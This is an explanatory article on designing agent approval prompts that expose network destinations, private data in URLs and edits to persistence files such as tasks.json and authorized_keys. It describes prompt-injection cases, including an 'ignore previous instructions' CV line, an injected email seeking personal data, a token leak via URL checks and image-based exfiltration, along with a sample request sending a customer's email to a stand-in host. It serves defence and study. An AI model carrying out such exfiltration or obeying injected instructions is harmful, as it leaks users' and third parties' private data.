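# Highlighting network destinations and sensitive file paths in agent approval prompts

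## What an approval prompt shows, and how an action can leak data or leave lasting changes

An approval prompt is a dialog that lets a person allow or refuse an action proposed by an AI agent, such as running a command or changing a file. Software companies use these prompts because agents make mistakes and outsiders can trick them. The danger of an action often depends on where it sends data and which files it reads or changes. Software can find these details in a proposed action and highlight them for the person, or it can block the action.

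### Agents, clients and tool calls

An agent is a language model that acts through software tools. The model only produces text, so it needs other software to act on that text. The *Request for Information Regarding Security Considerations for Artificial Intelligence Agents* (2026), a notice from the US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST), defines an agent system as at least one generative AI model plus "scaffolding software" that gives the model tools. The client is the part of this software that runs the agent, enforces the user's permissions and shows approval prompts. Examples include a code editor with a built-in agent and a chat application that can open web pages.

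A tool call is one action that the agent proposes. It consists of the name of a tool and a set of arguments, which are the values the tool needs. In Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026), a specification for connecting models to tools, the standard example is a tool with the name `get_weather` and one argument, `location`, set to New York. A call goes through these steps:

1. The model chooses a tool and writes the arguments.
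2. The client receives the proposed call and can check it or show it to the user.
3. The client sends the call to the server, the program that provides the tool.
4. The server returns a result. The client passes it to the model, which then chooses its next step.

The approval prompt appears in step 2, when the client has the tool's name and arguments but no reliable record of why the agent wants to make the call. Any explanation the agent offers may be wrong. In its security guidance for its code editor, VS Code, Microsoft therefore tells users to review the actual inputs as well as the agent's description of them.

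The Model Context Protocol recommends, but does not require, that clients show a tool's inputs to the user before the call, "to avoid malicious or accidental data exfiltration". The specification leaves the interface design to client developers, so two clients can show the same call quite differently. Some calls produce no prompt, because a permission setting or a saved approval already covers them, as VS Code's *Use tools with agents* explains.

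### How an ordinary task can lead to a harmful proposal

Outsiders can influence the agent at step 4. The result of a tool call may be a web page, an email or a file that a stranger wrote, and the model reads it along with the user's request. Prompt injection means hiding instructions in such content to redirect the agent.

In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, an article for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, David C describes a recruiter who uses a model to score job applications. One candidate hides a sentence in a CV telling the model to ignore its previous instructions and approve the candidate for interview. The recruiter meant the CV as data, but the model may treat the sentence as an instruction. Database software can be designed to keep commands and data apart, but a language model has no such boundary because it processes all its text the same way,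 by predicting what comes next. David C concludes that developers may never be able to prevent prompt injection completely, and that they should limit what a system can do when an injection succeeds.

Prompt injection can cause an agent to take a harmful action, not just produce a bad score. OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) reproduces an email that looks like a routine follow-up about a company restructuring. It contains instructions for the reader's AI assistant to find an employee's name and address in the mailbox and submit them to a "compliance validation system", along with a claim that the assistant is fully authorised to do so. In tests, the attack worked half the time when the user had asked for research on the day's emails. OpenAI describes such attacks as needing a source, which is a way to influence the agent, and a sink, which is a capability that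 becomes dangerous in the wrong context, such as sending information to a third party. An approval prompt is a check on the sink and does not address the source.

An agent can also propose a harmful action when no attacker is involved. NIST lists as a separate risk that an uncompromised model may still threaten the confidentiality or integrity of data. For example, an agent that pastes a whole error message into a search engine can leak any personal details in it. The tool call may be identical whether or not an attacker caused it, so the person approving it has to judge the action by its effects and cannot rely on spotting bad intent.

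### A running example

A developer asks an agent to find out why a build fails. (A build is the process that turns source code into a working program.) The agent reads the error log, which contains the email address of a real customer, Ana, because someone copied her record into a test. It also reads the help page of a package that the project uses. It then proposes three actions, and the client shows a bare prompt for each, with the type of action and its main argument in plain text:

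- **Action A.** Fetch `https://build-help.example.net/errors/lookup?code=1042&user=ana@example.com`
- **Action B.** Edit `.vscode/tasks.json`
- **Action C.** Run `./scripts/check-build.sh`

All three could be sensible steps towards fixing the build, but an instruction injected into the help page could also have caused any of them. The bare prompts would look the same in either case.

### Action A: sending data to a destination

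Exfiltration means sending private data to someone who should not have it. MITRE, a US research organisation that catalogues attackers' methods, defines it more narrowly as the techniques adversaries use to steal data from a network. The wider meaning is more useful for agents because a careless request exposes Ana's address just as a malicious one does.

Whether a transfer counts as exfiltration depends on who receives it. It is a breach if the agent sends Ana's email address to a stranger's server, but not if it sends the address to her supplier's own customer database. MITRE's catalogue names several techniques after the destination: a code repository, a cloud storage service, a site for sharing text, or a webhook (a web address that accepts automatic messages from other software). Attackers like popular services of this kind because the victim's machines often contact them anyway. Checking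 hosts against a trusted list can therefore miss data sent to a stranger's account on a familiar service.

Action A sends data out, even though it looks as if the agent is only reading a page. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) points out that opening a link sends the website the requested URL, and that websites commonly log these URLs. The site's owner can then read Ana's email address in the log, even if the page contains nothing useful or doesn't exist.

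WHATWG's *URL*, the technical standard for web addresses, gives the rules for splitting an address into parts. Four of them matter here:

| Part | In action A | What it does |
|---|---|---|
| Scheme | `https` | Identifies the type of address, and so how software should handle it |
| Host | `build-help.example.net` | Names the machine or service that the client contacts |
| Path | `/errors/lookup` | Usually identifies a location on that host, such as a page |
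| Query string | `code=1042&user=ana@example.com` | Carries data to the site, after the question mark |

An address can have other parts too, such as a port number after the host. To judge action A, the developer mainly has to look at the host, which determines who receives the request, and the query string, which here contains the private data. (A path can carry private data as well.)

The bare prompt for action A contains all of this if the client prints the whole address. The developer would still need to know who runs `example.net` and notice that the line ends with a customer's email address. It would also help to realize that the lookup probably does not need the email address, because the error code alone should be enough to find a help page. A developer who spots the problem can refuse and ask the agent to search again without the email address.

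### Action B: changing a file that another program will use

Persistence means that a change keeps having an effect after the action that made it ends. MITRE's *Persistence* defines the term by the attacker's aim of keeping access to a system across restarts, changed passwords and other interruptions. Attackers can do this by adding code that runs at start-up or changing a configuration file.

The danger of a file edit depends on the file. A command that an agent adds to meeting notes does nothing, but if the agent adds it to the start-up file of the shell (the program that interprets typed commands), the shell runs it whenever the user opens a new session. MITRE lists this as a known technique. The edit is harmless until another program reads the file and acts on it, which may be days later, when the agent is no longer running and the user has forgotten the prompt.

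The `.vscode` folder holds a project's VS Code settings, and its `tasks.json` file lists commands that the editor can run. According to VS Code's *Integrate with External Tools via Tasks*, an entry in this file can set its command to run as soon as someone opens the folder. The editor never runs such tasks in a project that the user has not marked as trusted. By default, it also asks once per project whether to allow them, so a developer who said yes months ago would not be asked again. The entry can also keep the editor from bringing the task's output to the front of the screen.

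The bare prompt for action B gives only the path. The developer would also need to know that the editor can run commands from this file, and to see which lines the agent wants to change. The path alone does not show whether the edit is legitimate, because a wrong command in `tasks.json` could easily explain a failing build. If the developer shares the project, colleagues who download it will get the new task too.

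### Reading a secret and writing a setting

Clients sometimes treat files as sensitive without distinguishing between reading and writing, though the two cause different kinds of harm. Reading a credential file, which contains passwords or access keys, leaves the file unchanged but adds its contents to the text the model works with. VS Code's *Understand trust and safety for AI agents* includes tool results among the material sent to the model, and the model may run on a provider's computers. The agent can also copy the key into any later tool call. Such a read is often the first step in an exfiltration, and the request that completes it may come several prompts later with no mention of the file.

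Writing to a configuration file requires no network destination. The harm occurs when a program later loads the file and follows its settings. A developer who notices the edit in time can undo it, but can't take back a password that has left the machine.

The `.ssh` folder in a user's home directory shows why the distinction is useful. It normally holds private keys for logging in to other computers, and the main risk is that someone reads them. It can also hold a file named `authorized_keys`, which lists the keys that may log in to the user's own account. The greater risk with that file is that someone adds a key. A safeguard against one risk may not protect against the other. In VS Code, for instance, the extra approval for edits to sensitive files does not restrict reading them.

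### Action C: a command that reveals very little

The bare prompt for action C shows the path of a script, but no host or other file. When the script runs, it could compile the program and print the errors, as its name suggests. It could also read a credential file, send the contents to `example.net` and edit `tasks.json`.

The script's name need not match its contents. The same is true of VS Code tasks, where the editor displays a label such as "Run tests" and a separate field holds the command. To judge action C, the developer would need to know what the script contains, which other programs it starts, and whether the agent has changed it since they last looked. An agent could edit an ordinary project file in one step and run it in the next, and neither prompt would look unusual.

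### Showing, highlighting and stopping

A client that wants to protect the developer can do three separate things with a detail such as the host in action A.

A prompt can show the detail, but not every prompt does. One that reads "Allow the agent to fetch a web page?" leaves out the host. A client that cuts addresses off after 50 characters would show the host and path of action A but not Ana's email address. Some rules deal only with showing the detail. For example, when a server asks a user to open a web address, the Model Context Protocol requires clients to display the target host clearly and get the user's consent.

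The client can highlight the detail with bold type, colour, position or a label such as "unknown site". To do this selectively, it must first flag the detail, or decide that this part of the call is sensitive. The client can show an address without making that decision.

The client can also block the action outright instead of waiting for the user to approve or reject it. Another option is to run a command inside a sandbox, where the operating system restricts access to files and network connections. In VS Code's documentation, approval controls whether an action can run without asking, and sandboxing controls what the process can reach once it runs. Even if a developer approves action C, the sandbox could still prevent the script from contacting `example.net`.

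A client can combine these measures or use any of them alone. It might print a host in red in the record of an action it has already allowed, or block a request without ever showing the address. Showing and highlighting protect Ana only if the developer reads the prompt, understands it and refuses. A block protects her even when the developer is not paying attention, but it also stops a request the developer needs if the client flags a harmless address by mistake.

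## Identifying the network destination and deciding whether it is trusted

Software can extract the host from a web address exactly. Deciding whether to trust whoever runs that host is harder, because it depends on lists that people write and on how much each entry covers.

The address in action A is `https://build-help.example.net/errors/lookup?code=1042&user=ana@example.com`. A client can check it in five steps:

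1. Parse the address, or split it into its parts, with software that follows the URL standard.
2. Take the host, `build-help.example.net`.
3. Reduce the host to its registrable domain, the part that someone registers and controls. Here that is `example.net`.
4. Compare the host with an allowlist, a list of hosts that need no approval. Suppose the developer's list contains only `docs.example.org`, where the package's authors publish their manual. The client finds no match and flags the address.
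5. If the developer approves the request and the server redirects it to another address, repeat the check on the new address.

### Parsing the address

The request in action A goes to `build-help.example.net`. Its address contains an @ sign, but the sign comes after the question mark, so it is ordinary data in the query string. Before the path of a web address, an @ sign separates an optional user name and password from the host that follows. A program that only looked for the @ sign would therefore return the wrong host, `example.com`, which is the domain of Ana's email address. A parser that follows the standard returns the correct host because it reads the address from left to right and tracks which part it has reached.

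WHATWG's host rules also convert different spellings of the same host into one. They lowercase letters, convert non-ASCII letters into an ASCII form that begins with `xn--`, and recognise numeric addresses in unusual notations. *Guidelines for URL Storage and Comparison* (2026), a guide by a Microsoft Defender engineer, lists several ways to write the address 127.0.0.2, including `2130706434` and `0x7f000002`. A client that compared the raw text would treat these as different hosts, and an attacker could use an unlisted spelling to get past a blocklist.

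URLs are easy to parse incorrectly. *Guidelines for URL Display* tells developers of Chromium, the open-source browser behind Google Chrome, to use only parsers that security specialists have reviewed and never to write their own clean-up code. Different programs can also parse the same unusual address differently, so the client should send the request to the parsed address it checked. If it passes the original text to a second program, that program may extract a different host.

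Two coding agents have had flaws because they skipped this step. GitHub's *Safeguarding VS Code against prompt injections* describes a 2025 security assessment of Copilot Chat, the extension that ran agents in VS Code. The agent's tool for fetching web pages asked for confirmation unless the site was on a list of trusted domains, which included several belonging to Microsoft and GitHub. The check compared the address with a text pattern instead of parsing it, so an address with a trusted name in the wrong part could pass. In the researcher's test, instructions hidden in a GitHub issue made the agent read an access token from a local file and send it to an outside website without any confirmation prompt.

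VS Code's developers responded by separating the fetch tool from the trusted-domains list, which they had designed for a different feature. They also required approval before the tool fetched any address for the first time. The researcher then found that a second tool, a small browser meant for testing local websites, could send the same data to an outside site without approval. Better parsing would not have fixed this, because the browser tool had no check on its destination. The developers added an approval prompt there as well.

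NIST's *CVE-2026-24052 Detail* records a similar error in Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent. Versions before 1.0.111 only checked whether an address started with the text of a trusted domain. Whoever registers a domain controls the host names that end in it, so an attacker could have registered one and put a trusted name in front of it. GitHub rated the flaw 7.1 out of 10 for severity, and Anthropic has since patched it. A client avoids both errors by parsing the address and then comparing complete hosts.

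### From the host to the registrable domain

Whoever registers `example.net` can create any name to the left of it, so the owner of `build-help.example.net` could just as easily have chosen the label `official-docs`. The registrable domain, `example.net`, leaves out these labels and identifies who is in control.

A client cannot find it by taking the last two labels of every host. That works for `example.net` but not for `www.bbc.co.uk`, because many unrelated organisations register names under `co.uk`. Each registry makes its own rules about this, so software has to look them up. The Public Suffix List, which Mozilla volunteers maintain with submissions from registries, records the endings under which separate parties can register names. The registrable domain is the public suffix plus one more label:

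| Host | Public suffix | Registrable domain |
|---|---|---|
| `build-help.example.net` | `net` | `example.net` |
| `www.bbc.co.uk` | `co.uk` | `bbc.co.uk` |
| `whatwg.github.io` | `github.io` | `whatwg.github.io` |
| `github.io` | `github.io` | none |
| A numeric IP address | none | none |

Developers have to decide what to do when the lookup finds no answer. MDN, Mozilla's reference site for web developers, documents a browser function for this lookup with two options for such cases, both off by default. One returns a numeric address unchanged, and the other falls back on the last two labels when the list has no matching suffix. In an approval prompt, showing the full host is safer, since a guessed domain could identify the wrong owner.

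The list also changes over time, and a program with an old copy may split a host in the wrong place. WHATWG warns that copies differ between clients, so the registrable domain cannot be a hard security boundary. It recommends basing security decisions on the origin, the combination of scheme, host and port. The registrable domain is more useful for showing users who controls a site than for deciding which requests may skip a prompt.

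### Comparing the host with an allowlist

An allowlist entry can match one exact host, or it can extend to subdomains, other ports and every path on the site. *Guidelines for URL Storage and Comparison* calls this extension "roll-up" and cites SmartScreen, Microsoft's filter for dangerous websites, where a rule that blocks `https://x.com` also blocks `http://x.com:12345`. One reason is that ports on the same host rarely have different owners.

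Broad matching suits a blocklist because a mistake usually results in an unnecessary block. On an allowlist, every additional match is an address that the agent can contact without asking. For example, if an entry for an https site also matches plain http, the agent can send requests that other people on the network may be able to read or change. Someone who trusts the site over https has not necessarily accepted that risk.

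Wildcards, which match any name in a given position, need similar care. An entry for `*.github.com` covers hosts that GitHub controls, while `*.github.io` covers websites belonging to GitHub's users. According to the Public Suffix List, some network firewalls use the list to reject entries like `*.github.io`.

An entry that names a path should match whole segments, the pieces between slashes. An entry for `/foo` should not match `/foobar`, which begins with the same text but is a different location. WHATWG advises against path-based trust in most cases, because the rest of the web treats everything on a host as belonging together.

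### Following redirects

A server can redirect a request to another address, and much software follows redirects automatically. The client may then contact a second host that the user did not approve. The first server has already received the query string and can copy it into the new address.

Suppose `build-help.example.net` redirects action A to `docs.example.org`. The final host is on the developer's allowlist, but the first host has already received Ana's email address. If the redirect is reversed, the agent goes from a trusted site to an untrusted one. A client therefore has to check the first address before sending anything and each later address before following the redirect.

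OpenAI decided against relying on a list of well-known sites partly because many legitimate sites redirect visitors, so a link to a trusted host can lead to an untrusted one, according to the marketing company Stan Ventures. OpenAI also worried that strict lists would produce frequent warnings that people learn to ignore. It instead checks whether the complete address already appears in a public index of the web.

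Some clients stop when a redirect leads to a different host. *Inside Claude Code's Web Tools* (2025), based on observing the program as it ran, found that Claude Code's fetch tool automatically follows redirects that stay on the same host. According to unofficial documentation hosted by Mintlify, if the host changes, the tool gives the new address to the model, which has to make a new fetch request. That request gives the client another chance to check the destination.

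An agent can also send an access key to the wrong host. Clients often send keys in headers, which are fields that accompany a request but do not appear in its address. Docker, a container software company, has its agent's fetch tool remove user-added headers when a request is redirected to another host. It still recommends listing the hosts that may receive a key, because removing headers on a redirect doesn't protect the key if the first request goes to the wrong host.

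### Two customers of one hosting service

The checks so far rely on each host or domain belonging to one party. Suppose a hosting service gives every customer a website under `pages.example`. The developer's employer uses `acme.pages.example`, and a stranger signs up and gets `northside.pages.example`.

If the service's domain, `pages.example`, is on the Public Suffix List, the employer's and the stranger's hosts have different registrable domains. If it is not, both hosts reduce to `pages.example`, and a prompt that highlights only the registrable domain highlights the same text for both.

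M3AAWG, an industry group that works against online abuse, notes that cloud providers and content delivery networks often put many customers on shared domains. The Public Suffix List has a PRIVATE section for such domains. Mozilla's *Public Suffix List/Uses* explains that some domain owners give subdomains to parties that do not trust each other, and names Amazon, Google and GitHub among the companies with entries. But hosting companies have to submit their own domains, so a client cannot assume that the list covers every service.

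Other services separate customers by path. The employer might upload files to `https://files.example/acme/` and the stranger to `https://files.example/northside/`. These URLs have the same host, so no version of the Public Suffix List can separate them, and an allowlist entry for `files.example` covers both. A path rule makes sense here, despite WHATWG's general advice, if the service assigns each path to one customer.

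On some services, even the complete address does not identify the recipient, because an access key sent with the request determines whose account receives the data. The client would need to work out which account the key belongs to, or tell the user that it can identify the service but not the recipient.

### Which parts of an address mislead readers

A person may misread an address that the client has parsed correctly. People tend to look for a familiar name, and a site's owner can put one almost anywhere:

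- In a long subdomain, as in `docs.example.org.errors.example.net`. The site belongs to whoever controls `example.net`, although the trusted name comes first.
- Before an @ sign, as in `https://docs.example.org@example.net/`. The trusted name is only a user name here.
- In the path, as in `https://example.net/docs.example.org/help`. The owner of `example.net` chooses the path.
- In lookalike characters. The letters `rn` can resemble `m`, and the Cyrillic letter а looks the same as the Latin one in many fonts.

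Invisible characters can also push the real host out of view, and a padlock emoji in an address may look like the browser's security symbol.

Chromium recommends showing only the origin when people have to make a security decision, or only the domain if the connection always uses https. It tells developers to leave out user names, paths and query strings because attackers can use them to deceive people. If space is short, the registrable domain alone is acceptable. When developers have to show the full address, Chromium suggests highlighting only the registrable domain. It also gives rules for when to display the `xn--` form of a host, which is hard to read but doesn't look like a familiar name.

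Shortening a hostname can mislead users. A proposed text for WHATWG's standard, on which van Kesteren (2019) commented, gives the example of `not-really-examplecorp.com`, which careless shortening might turn into `...examplecorp.com`. The proposal requires enough room to show the whole registrable domain. If the full host still does not fit, the program should remove whole labels from the front.

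These rules come from browsers, where the usual concern is who supplied the page. The developer reviewing action A also has to judge what the agent is about to send. A prompt that followed Chromium's advice literally would show `build-help.example.net` and hide Ana's email address. An approval prompt should therefore show the destination on its own line, with its registrable domain highlighted, and show the outgoing data separately.

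This may not change people's decisions. gHacks' *Google ends Simplified URL experiment in Chrome* (2021) reported that Google tried showing only the domain in Chrome's address bar and ended the experiment in 2021 because security metrics had not improved. A correctly displayed name can also be deceptive. Chromium's guidance does not cover domains such as `google-update.com`, which look plausible but have no connection to Google, and notes that browsers rely on users to recognise them. In action A, highlighting `example.net` would not show the developer whether the package's authors have any connection to that domain.

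### Destinations that are not web addresses

Agents also send data with commands that give only a short name for the destination. Git, for example, stores the addresses of other copies of a project under nicknames called remotes, so `git push origin main` sends code to whatever address the project's configuration gives for `origin`. The client has to look up that address to show the host. It may also need a separate parser, because Git accepts addresses such as `git@example.net:team/project.git`, which the URL standard's parser rejects.

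A remote's nickname can stay the same while its address changes. An agent could point `origin` at another server and then push, and the prompt for the push would look the same as before the change. Anthropic's *Choose a permission mode* describes two defences in Claude Code's auto mode, in which a classifier (a second model that judges proposed actions) replaces most prompts. The classifier does not trust a remote that the agent added or changed during the session. By default, it also blocks commands that change where pushes go, unless the user has named the new remote. Before version 2.1.200, the classifier trusted remotes added during a session.

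An email domain is often too broad to identify the destination, because millions of unrelated people have addresses at the large email providers. The client should therefore show the complete address of every recipient, including anyone copied. A link that opens a new email, such as `mailto:ana@example.com?subject=Build`, has a different structure from a web address. The standard parser returns no host for it, so the client needs separate rules to extract the recipient.

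Whether a recipient is appropriate can depend on what is being sent. Under Claude Code's default rules, the classifier blocks a message that includes sensitive details unless the user authorised sending those details to that recipient. For example, approval to email a colleague about the failed build would not automatically cover sending them Ana's record.

Developers download shared code from package registries. An install command usually specifies the package, while a configuration file or a built-in default determines the registry. Changing the registry setting can make the same command download code from a stranger. By default, Claude Code blocks the agent from pointing a registry setting at an outside host that does not fit the task. It also blocks installs that bypass a company's internal registry and use a public one, if the user has said that an internal registry exists.

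An agent can also send data to a registry. Many public registries let anyone with an account publish packages, so a registry that is a sensible source of downloads may be an unsafe place to upload private code. An allowlist entry that contains only the host does not distinguish between downloads and uploads.

### What a saved approval covers

Most clients let users save an approval so that the same prompt does not keep appearing. The scope of that approval then decides which later requests go through unseen, and products differ a good deal:

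| Client | What the rule or saved approval covers | Where it applies |
|---|---|---|
| VS Code, Copilot sessions | The displayed host only | One session, or future sessions on the same agent host |
| VS Code, older Local sessions | A URL or domain, with separate approvals for the request and the response | Future requests or responses |
| Copilot CLI | The domain of the approved address | All sessions |
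| GitHub's cloud agent | A domain and its subdomains, or a URL and the paths below it | The repository with that setting |
| Claude Code's auto mode | The project's git remotes at the start of the session, plus any infrastructure that the user lists | The session for the remotes, and the chosen settings for the list |

According to Microsoft's *Manage approvals and permissions*, approval for `https://example.com` in VS Code does not currently extend to `http://example.com` or `https://sub.example.com`. If the developer allowed `build-help.example.net`, a request to another host under `example.net` would produce a new prompt. This rule adds some clicks but avoids depending on the Public Suffix List to decide which hosts belong together.

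The Local harness, an older system for running agents in VS Code that Microsoft will remove in February 2027, requires one approval for the client to contact a site (request approval) and another for the page's contents to enter the conversation (response approval). With an ordinary approval prompt, the user can check only where data goes, but response approval also gives them a chance to catch injected instructions before the model reads them.

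In these older sessions, requests to any site on VS Code's Trusted Domains list skip approval, but the responses still need review. GitHub had described separating the fetch tool from this list as part of the fix for the 2025 flaw. Using the list again lets an agent send requests without a prompt to domains that someone trusted for another purpose, though it does not by itself bring back the parsing error.

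According to GitHub's *Allowing and denying tool use*, saved permission for a command or file change in Copilot CLI, GitHub's command-line agent, applies to one repository or directory, while permanent approval of a URL adds its domain to a list that applies to every session. A developer who permanently approves a help site while working on a hobby project would therefore not see a prompt for it later when working on a confidential one.

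GitHub's cloud agent runs on GitHub's servers behind a firewall that allows or blocks network connections without asking anyone. GitHub's recommended allowlist is on by default and includes package registries for popular programming languages and other common sources of software. Repository owners can add a domain, which also allows its subdomains, or a URL, which limits access to one scheme, host and path. If the firewall blocks a request, the agent's pull request (its proposal to change the code) includes a warning that shows the blocked address and the command that made the request.

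The firewall covers only programs that the agent starts through its command-line tool, not Model Context Protocol servers or the steps that prepare the agent's environment. GitHub also warns that sophisticated attacks may bypass it.

Claude Code's auto mode starts with a much smaller set of trusted places, consisting of the agent's working folder and the git remotes configured for it when the session begins. It treats everything else as external. Anthropic's *Configure auto mode* explains how users can add repositories, internal domains, cloud storage and a package registry by describing them in ordinary sentences, which the classifier treats as rules. Public sites for sharing text remain external unless a user names one. The classifier ignores trust rules in a project's own settings files, because a downloaded project could otherwise mark its author's server as trusted.

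Auto mode can allow a request to a destination it treats as external. By default, it allows read-only web requests and blocks sending sensitive data to external sites. Action A fits both descriptions because it fetches a page and sends Ana's email address in the query string. The result depends on whether the classifier detects the email address.

When a sandboxed command requests network access in auto mode, the classifier's approval for that host and port lasts only until new content enters the conversation. Checking again at that point is sensible because the new content may contain an injected instruction.

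A saved approval for a host, even one scoped as narrowly as VS Code's, also covers later requests that send private data to that host. Suppose the agent first asks to fetch `https://build-help.example.net/errors/lookup?code=1042`, which contains only the error code. The developer sees nothing private and chooses to always allow the host. If the agent later adds `&user=ana@example.com`, the saved approval still applies because the host is the same, and the agent sends Ana's email address without a prompt.

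## Detecting private data inside a web address

A client has to examine the whole web address of every request, even one to an approved host, to detect that the agent has added Ana's email address.

### Why the request itself is the leak

A server needs the path and query string to decide which page to return, so it receives any private data in them before the agent has anything to read. An agent could put a whole email into one address, since the IETF's HTTP standard recommends support for request addresses of at least 8,000 bytes, enough for about a thousand words of plain English.

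People other than the site's owner may also get a copy. The IETF adds that software is more likely to log a request's address than its content, and that addresses can turn up in bookmarks. OWASP, a software security non-profit, also lists browser history and the logs of any proxies in its rule *9.3 Sensitive data does not get sent in the URL*. It recommends that developers send sensitive data in the body or headers of a request instead. This keeps the data away from third parties when the recipient is legitimate. If the recipient is a stranger, moving Ana's email address into the body doesn't protect it, and a client that inspects only web addresses would no longer find it.

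### Images and link previews

An agent can cause a web request without calling a fetch tool. If its reply includes an image from the web, the program that displays the reply requests the image's address to load it. An injected instruction can make the model put private data in that address, and displaying the reply then sends the data to the server named in the address.

*OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, a post on Embrace The Red, a security researcher's blog, says that its author reported this kind of leak to OpenAI in early 2023. The author also told Microsoft, whose Bing Chat had the same problem, and Microsoft restricted image loading that May. OpenAI added its first protection in December 2023, but it did not initially cover some places, including the macOS and iOS apps.

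Every program that displays the model's text needs the protection. *OpenAI API Logs*, a report by the security company PromptArmor, describes a leak through the page where developers review their models' past replies. Even if an application refused to display a suspicious image, the log viewer would still load it when a developer opened the reply. OpenAI confirmed the flaw after the report came out and began work on a fix.

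Link previews can also leak data without a click. Chat applications such as Slack and Telegram fetch links to show a title and a thumbnail. According to PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps*, a preview makes the same type of request as a click, so the data leaks as soon as the agent posts the message. PromptArmor found that OpenClaw, an agent that people can use through chat applications, was open to this attack with its default Telegram settings. Setting `linkPreview` to `false` prevents it. In *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks and what to do*, Willison (2024) relays a similar fix for Slack, where an application can turn off previews for the messages it posts.

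An approval prompt may never appear when the agent only writes a reply containing a web address and another program makes the request. A client therefore has to check the addresses in the agent's text before displaying or posting it, as well as those in the agent's tool calls.

### Four ways to check an address

| Check | Input | Rule | Output | Typical error |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Known patterns | The address | Flag text in the format of a secret or personal detail | The matching text | Misses data in an unlisted or altered format |
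| Length or randomness | The address or the values in its query string | Flag anything over a set limit | A number and a yes or no | Flags harmless identifiers and misses short or readable data |
| Comparison with data the agent has seen | The address and the text the agent has read | Flag text that appears in both | The matching text and its source | Flags harmless shared text and misses rewritten data |
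| Public-address check | The address and an index of public addresses | Flag any address that is not in the index | A yes or no | Flags harmless addresses that the index lacks |

### Known patterns

In *Silent Egress*, Lan, Kaul and colleagues (2026) tested a simple pattern filter that blocked addresses containing words such as `api_key`, `password`, `token` or `auth`, or the text `key=sk-`, which resembles the start of some access keys. Action A contains none of these, so the filter would let it through. If the filter also had a pattern for email addresses, it would flag `ana@example.com`, and the client could highlight just that text.

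The result depends on which patterns the filter's author included. A filter can recognise email addresses and payment card numbers by their form, but not a sentence about someone's illness. Short patterns also match harmless text. For example, `auth` appears in `authors`, so a filter that searched the whole address for it would block a page that lists a package's authors.

A web address can also contain the same data in a different form, such as `%40` in place of an @ sign, so a client should decode the address before looking for matches. An attacker can still inject an instruction for the model to disguise the data in ways that the client does not decode.

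A service can help software recognise its access keys as secrets by starting each key with `secret-token:`, a standard label that Nottingham describes. The label is meant to reduce accidental disclosure. It cannot prevent intentional disclosure, since an attacker can tell the agent to leave the label out.

### Length and randomness

Access keys usually look random, and a client can measure this without knowing a key's format. A common measure is Shannon entropy, which is higher when a value uses many different characters about equally often:

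H = −Σ pᵢ log₂ pᵢ

Here pᵢ is the fraction of the value's characters that are character i. A value that repeats one character scores 0. A value of n characters scores at most log₂ n, when all its characters are different.

Lan and colleagues set their filter to block any value longer than 10 characters that scored above 4.0. In action A, `ana@example.com` has 15 characters. The letter a appears three times, e and m each appear twice, and eight other characters appear once. The score is about 3.3, so the filter would let the request through.

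The filter could not have flagged any 15-character value, because the maximum score at that length is about 3.9. A value needs at least 17 characters to score above 4.0, so the filter's 10-character minimum has no effect. Even the 20-character `SECRET_API_KEY_12345`, a sample key used elsewhere in the paper, scores only about 3.8.

With a lower limit, the filter would catch Ana's email address but also many harmless values, because ordinary links often contain long random identifiers. Pulse Security's *Sensitive data in URLs* gives the example of an accounting service that emails customers invoice links that end in an unguessable identifier. A randomness filter cannot distinguish that identifier from a stolen key.

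A simpler method is to limit the length of the address. Anthropic's fetch tool for developers rejects addresses longer than 250 characters, according to *Web fetch tool*. The address in Action A has 75 characters, so it would pass. The limit restricts how much an agent can send at once, but most private details are short enough to fit.

### Comparison with data the agent has seen

A client can keep the text the agent has read and search it for each value in an outgoing address. Ana's email address appears in the error log, so the client would find a match in action A and could tell the developer that the request contains an email address from the log. This check doesn't rely on a list of formats, so it could also catch a customer's name or the title of an unannounced project.

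But `1042` also comes from the error log, and the agent has to send it to look up the error. A comparison finds both values without distinguishing them. The client needs another rule, such as ignoring short numbers, and each such rule lets some private data through. A plain text search also misses data that the agent has reworded or encoded.

Lan and colleagues propose tracking where a request came from instead. The client would label everything from a web page as untrusted and extend that label to any tool argument the content influenced. When a labelled argument reached a tool with network access, the client could block the call or ask the user. If the help page had prompted action A, the client could flag the request no matter how the agent had disguised Ana's email address. Lan and colleagues did not build this system. It would be difficult to build because a language model processes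 all its text together, which makes it hard to establish which parts influenced a given output.

### Splitting the data over several requests

Pattern and randomness filters usually examine one address at a time, so an attacker can evade them by having the agent send a secret in pieces. A fragment such as `SECR` matches no pattern for a key, and the entropy of four characters is at most 2 bits per character.

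The experiment by Lan and colleagues, who work at eBay, measured how an agent behaves under such instructions. They used Qwen2.5 7B, a small open model, and placed a made-up secret in the text it was working with. In every run, the user asked the agent to summarise a web page. The page contained an instruction to send the secret to the attacker's server. The authors varied three things:

- the instruction's position, which was the page's title, its description, its body or the text of a link
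- the route to the page, either direct or through redirects
- the form of the leak, with the secret either whole or in four pieces

The experiment included 30 runs of each of the 16 combinations, 480 in total, and recorded what reached the attacker's server. The agent contacted the server in 423 runs, or 88%. In 95% of the successful attacks, the agent's final answer looked harmless. In 120 further runs with ordinary pages, the agent never contacted the server.

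In the same study, the first outgoing request contained sensitive data in 96.7% of runs when the agent sent the secret whole, but in only 26.3% when it sent the secret in pieces. This 73% drop measures how much less often there was sensitive data for a filter to find in that request, not how much less data the attacker received. Some of the drop reflects failed attacks, because the agent contacted the server in only about 77% of the runs with a split secret, compared with 99% of the others. Among runs where it did contact the server, the rate fell from about 97% to about 34%.

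The exact figures warrant some caution. For split secrets, the paper reports a lower rate for the first three requests together (15.8%) than for the first request alone (26.3%). This is impossible by the paper's own definition, because the first three requests include the first. The paper also does not report how often all four pieces arrived.

In a separate test, they compared defences against one version of the attack, with the instruction in the page's body and the secret sent whole. They ran each defence 30 times:

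| Defence | Runs in which the agent tried to send data | Runs in which data reached the attacker |
|---|---|---|
| None | 30 | 30 |
| Telling the model to ignore instructions in web content | 20 | 20 |
| Marking web content as untrusted | 30 | 30 |
| Both of these measures | 17 | 17 |
| Allowlist of domains | 30 | 0 |
| Filter for suspicious destinations | 25 | 0 |
| Keyword filter | 7 | 0 |
| Randomness filter | 0 | 0 |
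| All defences together | 0 | 0 |

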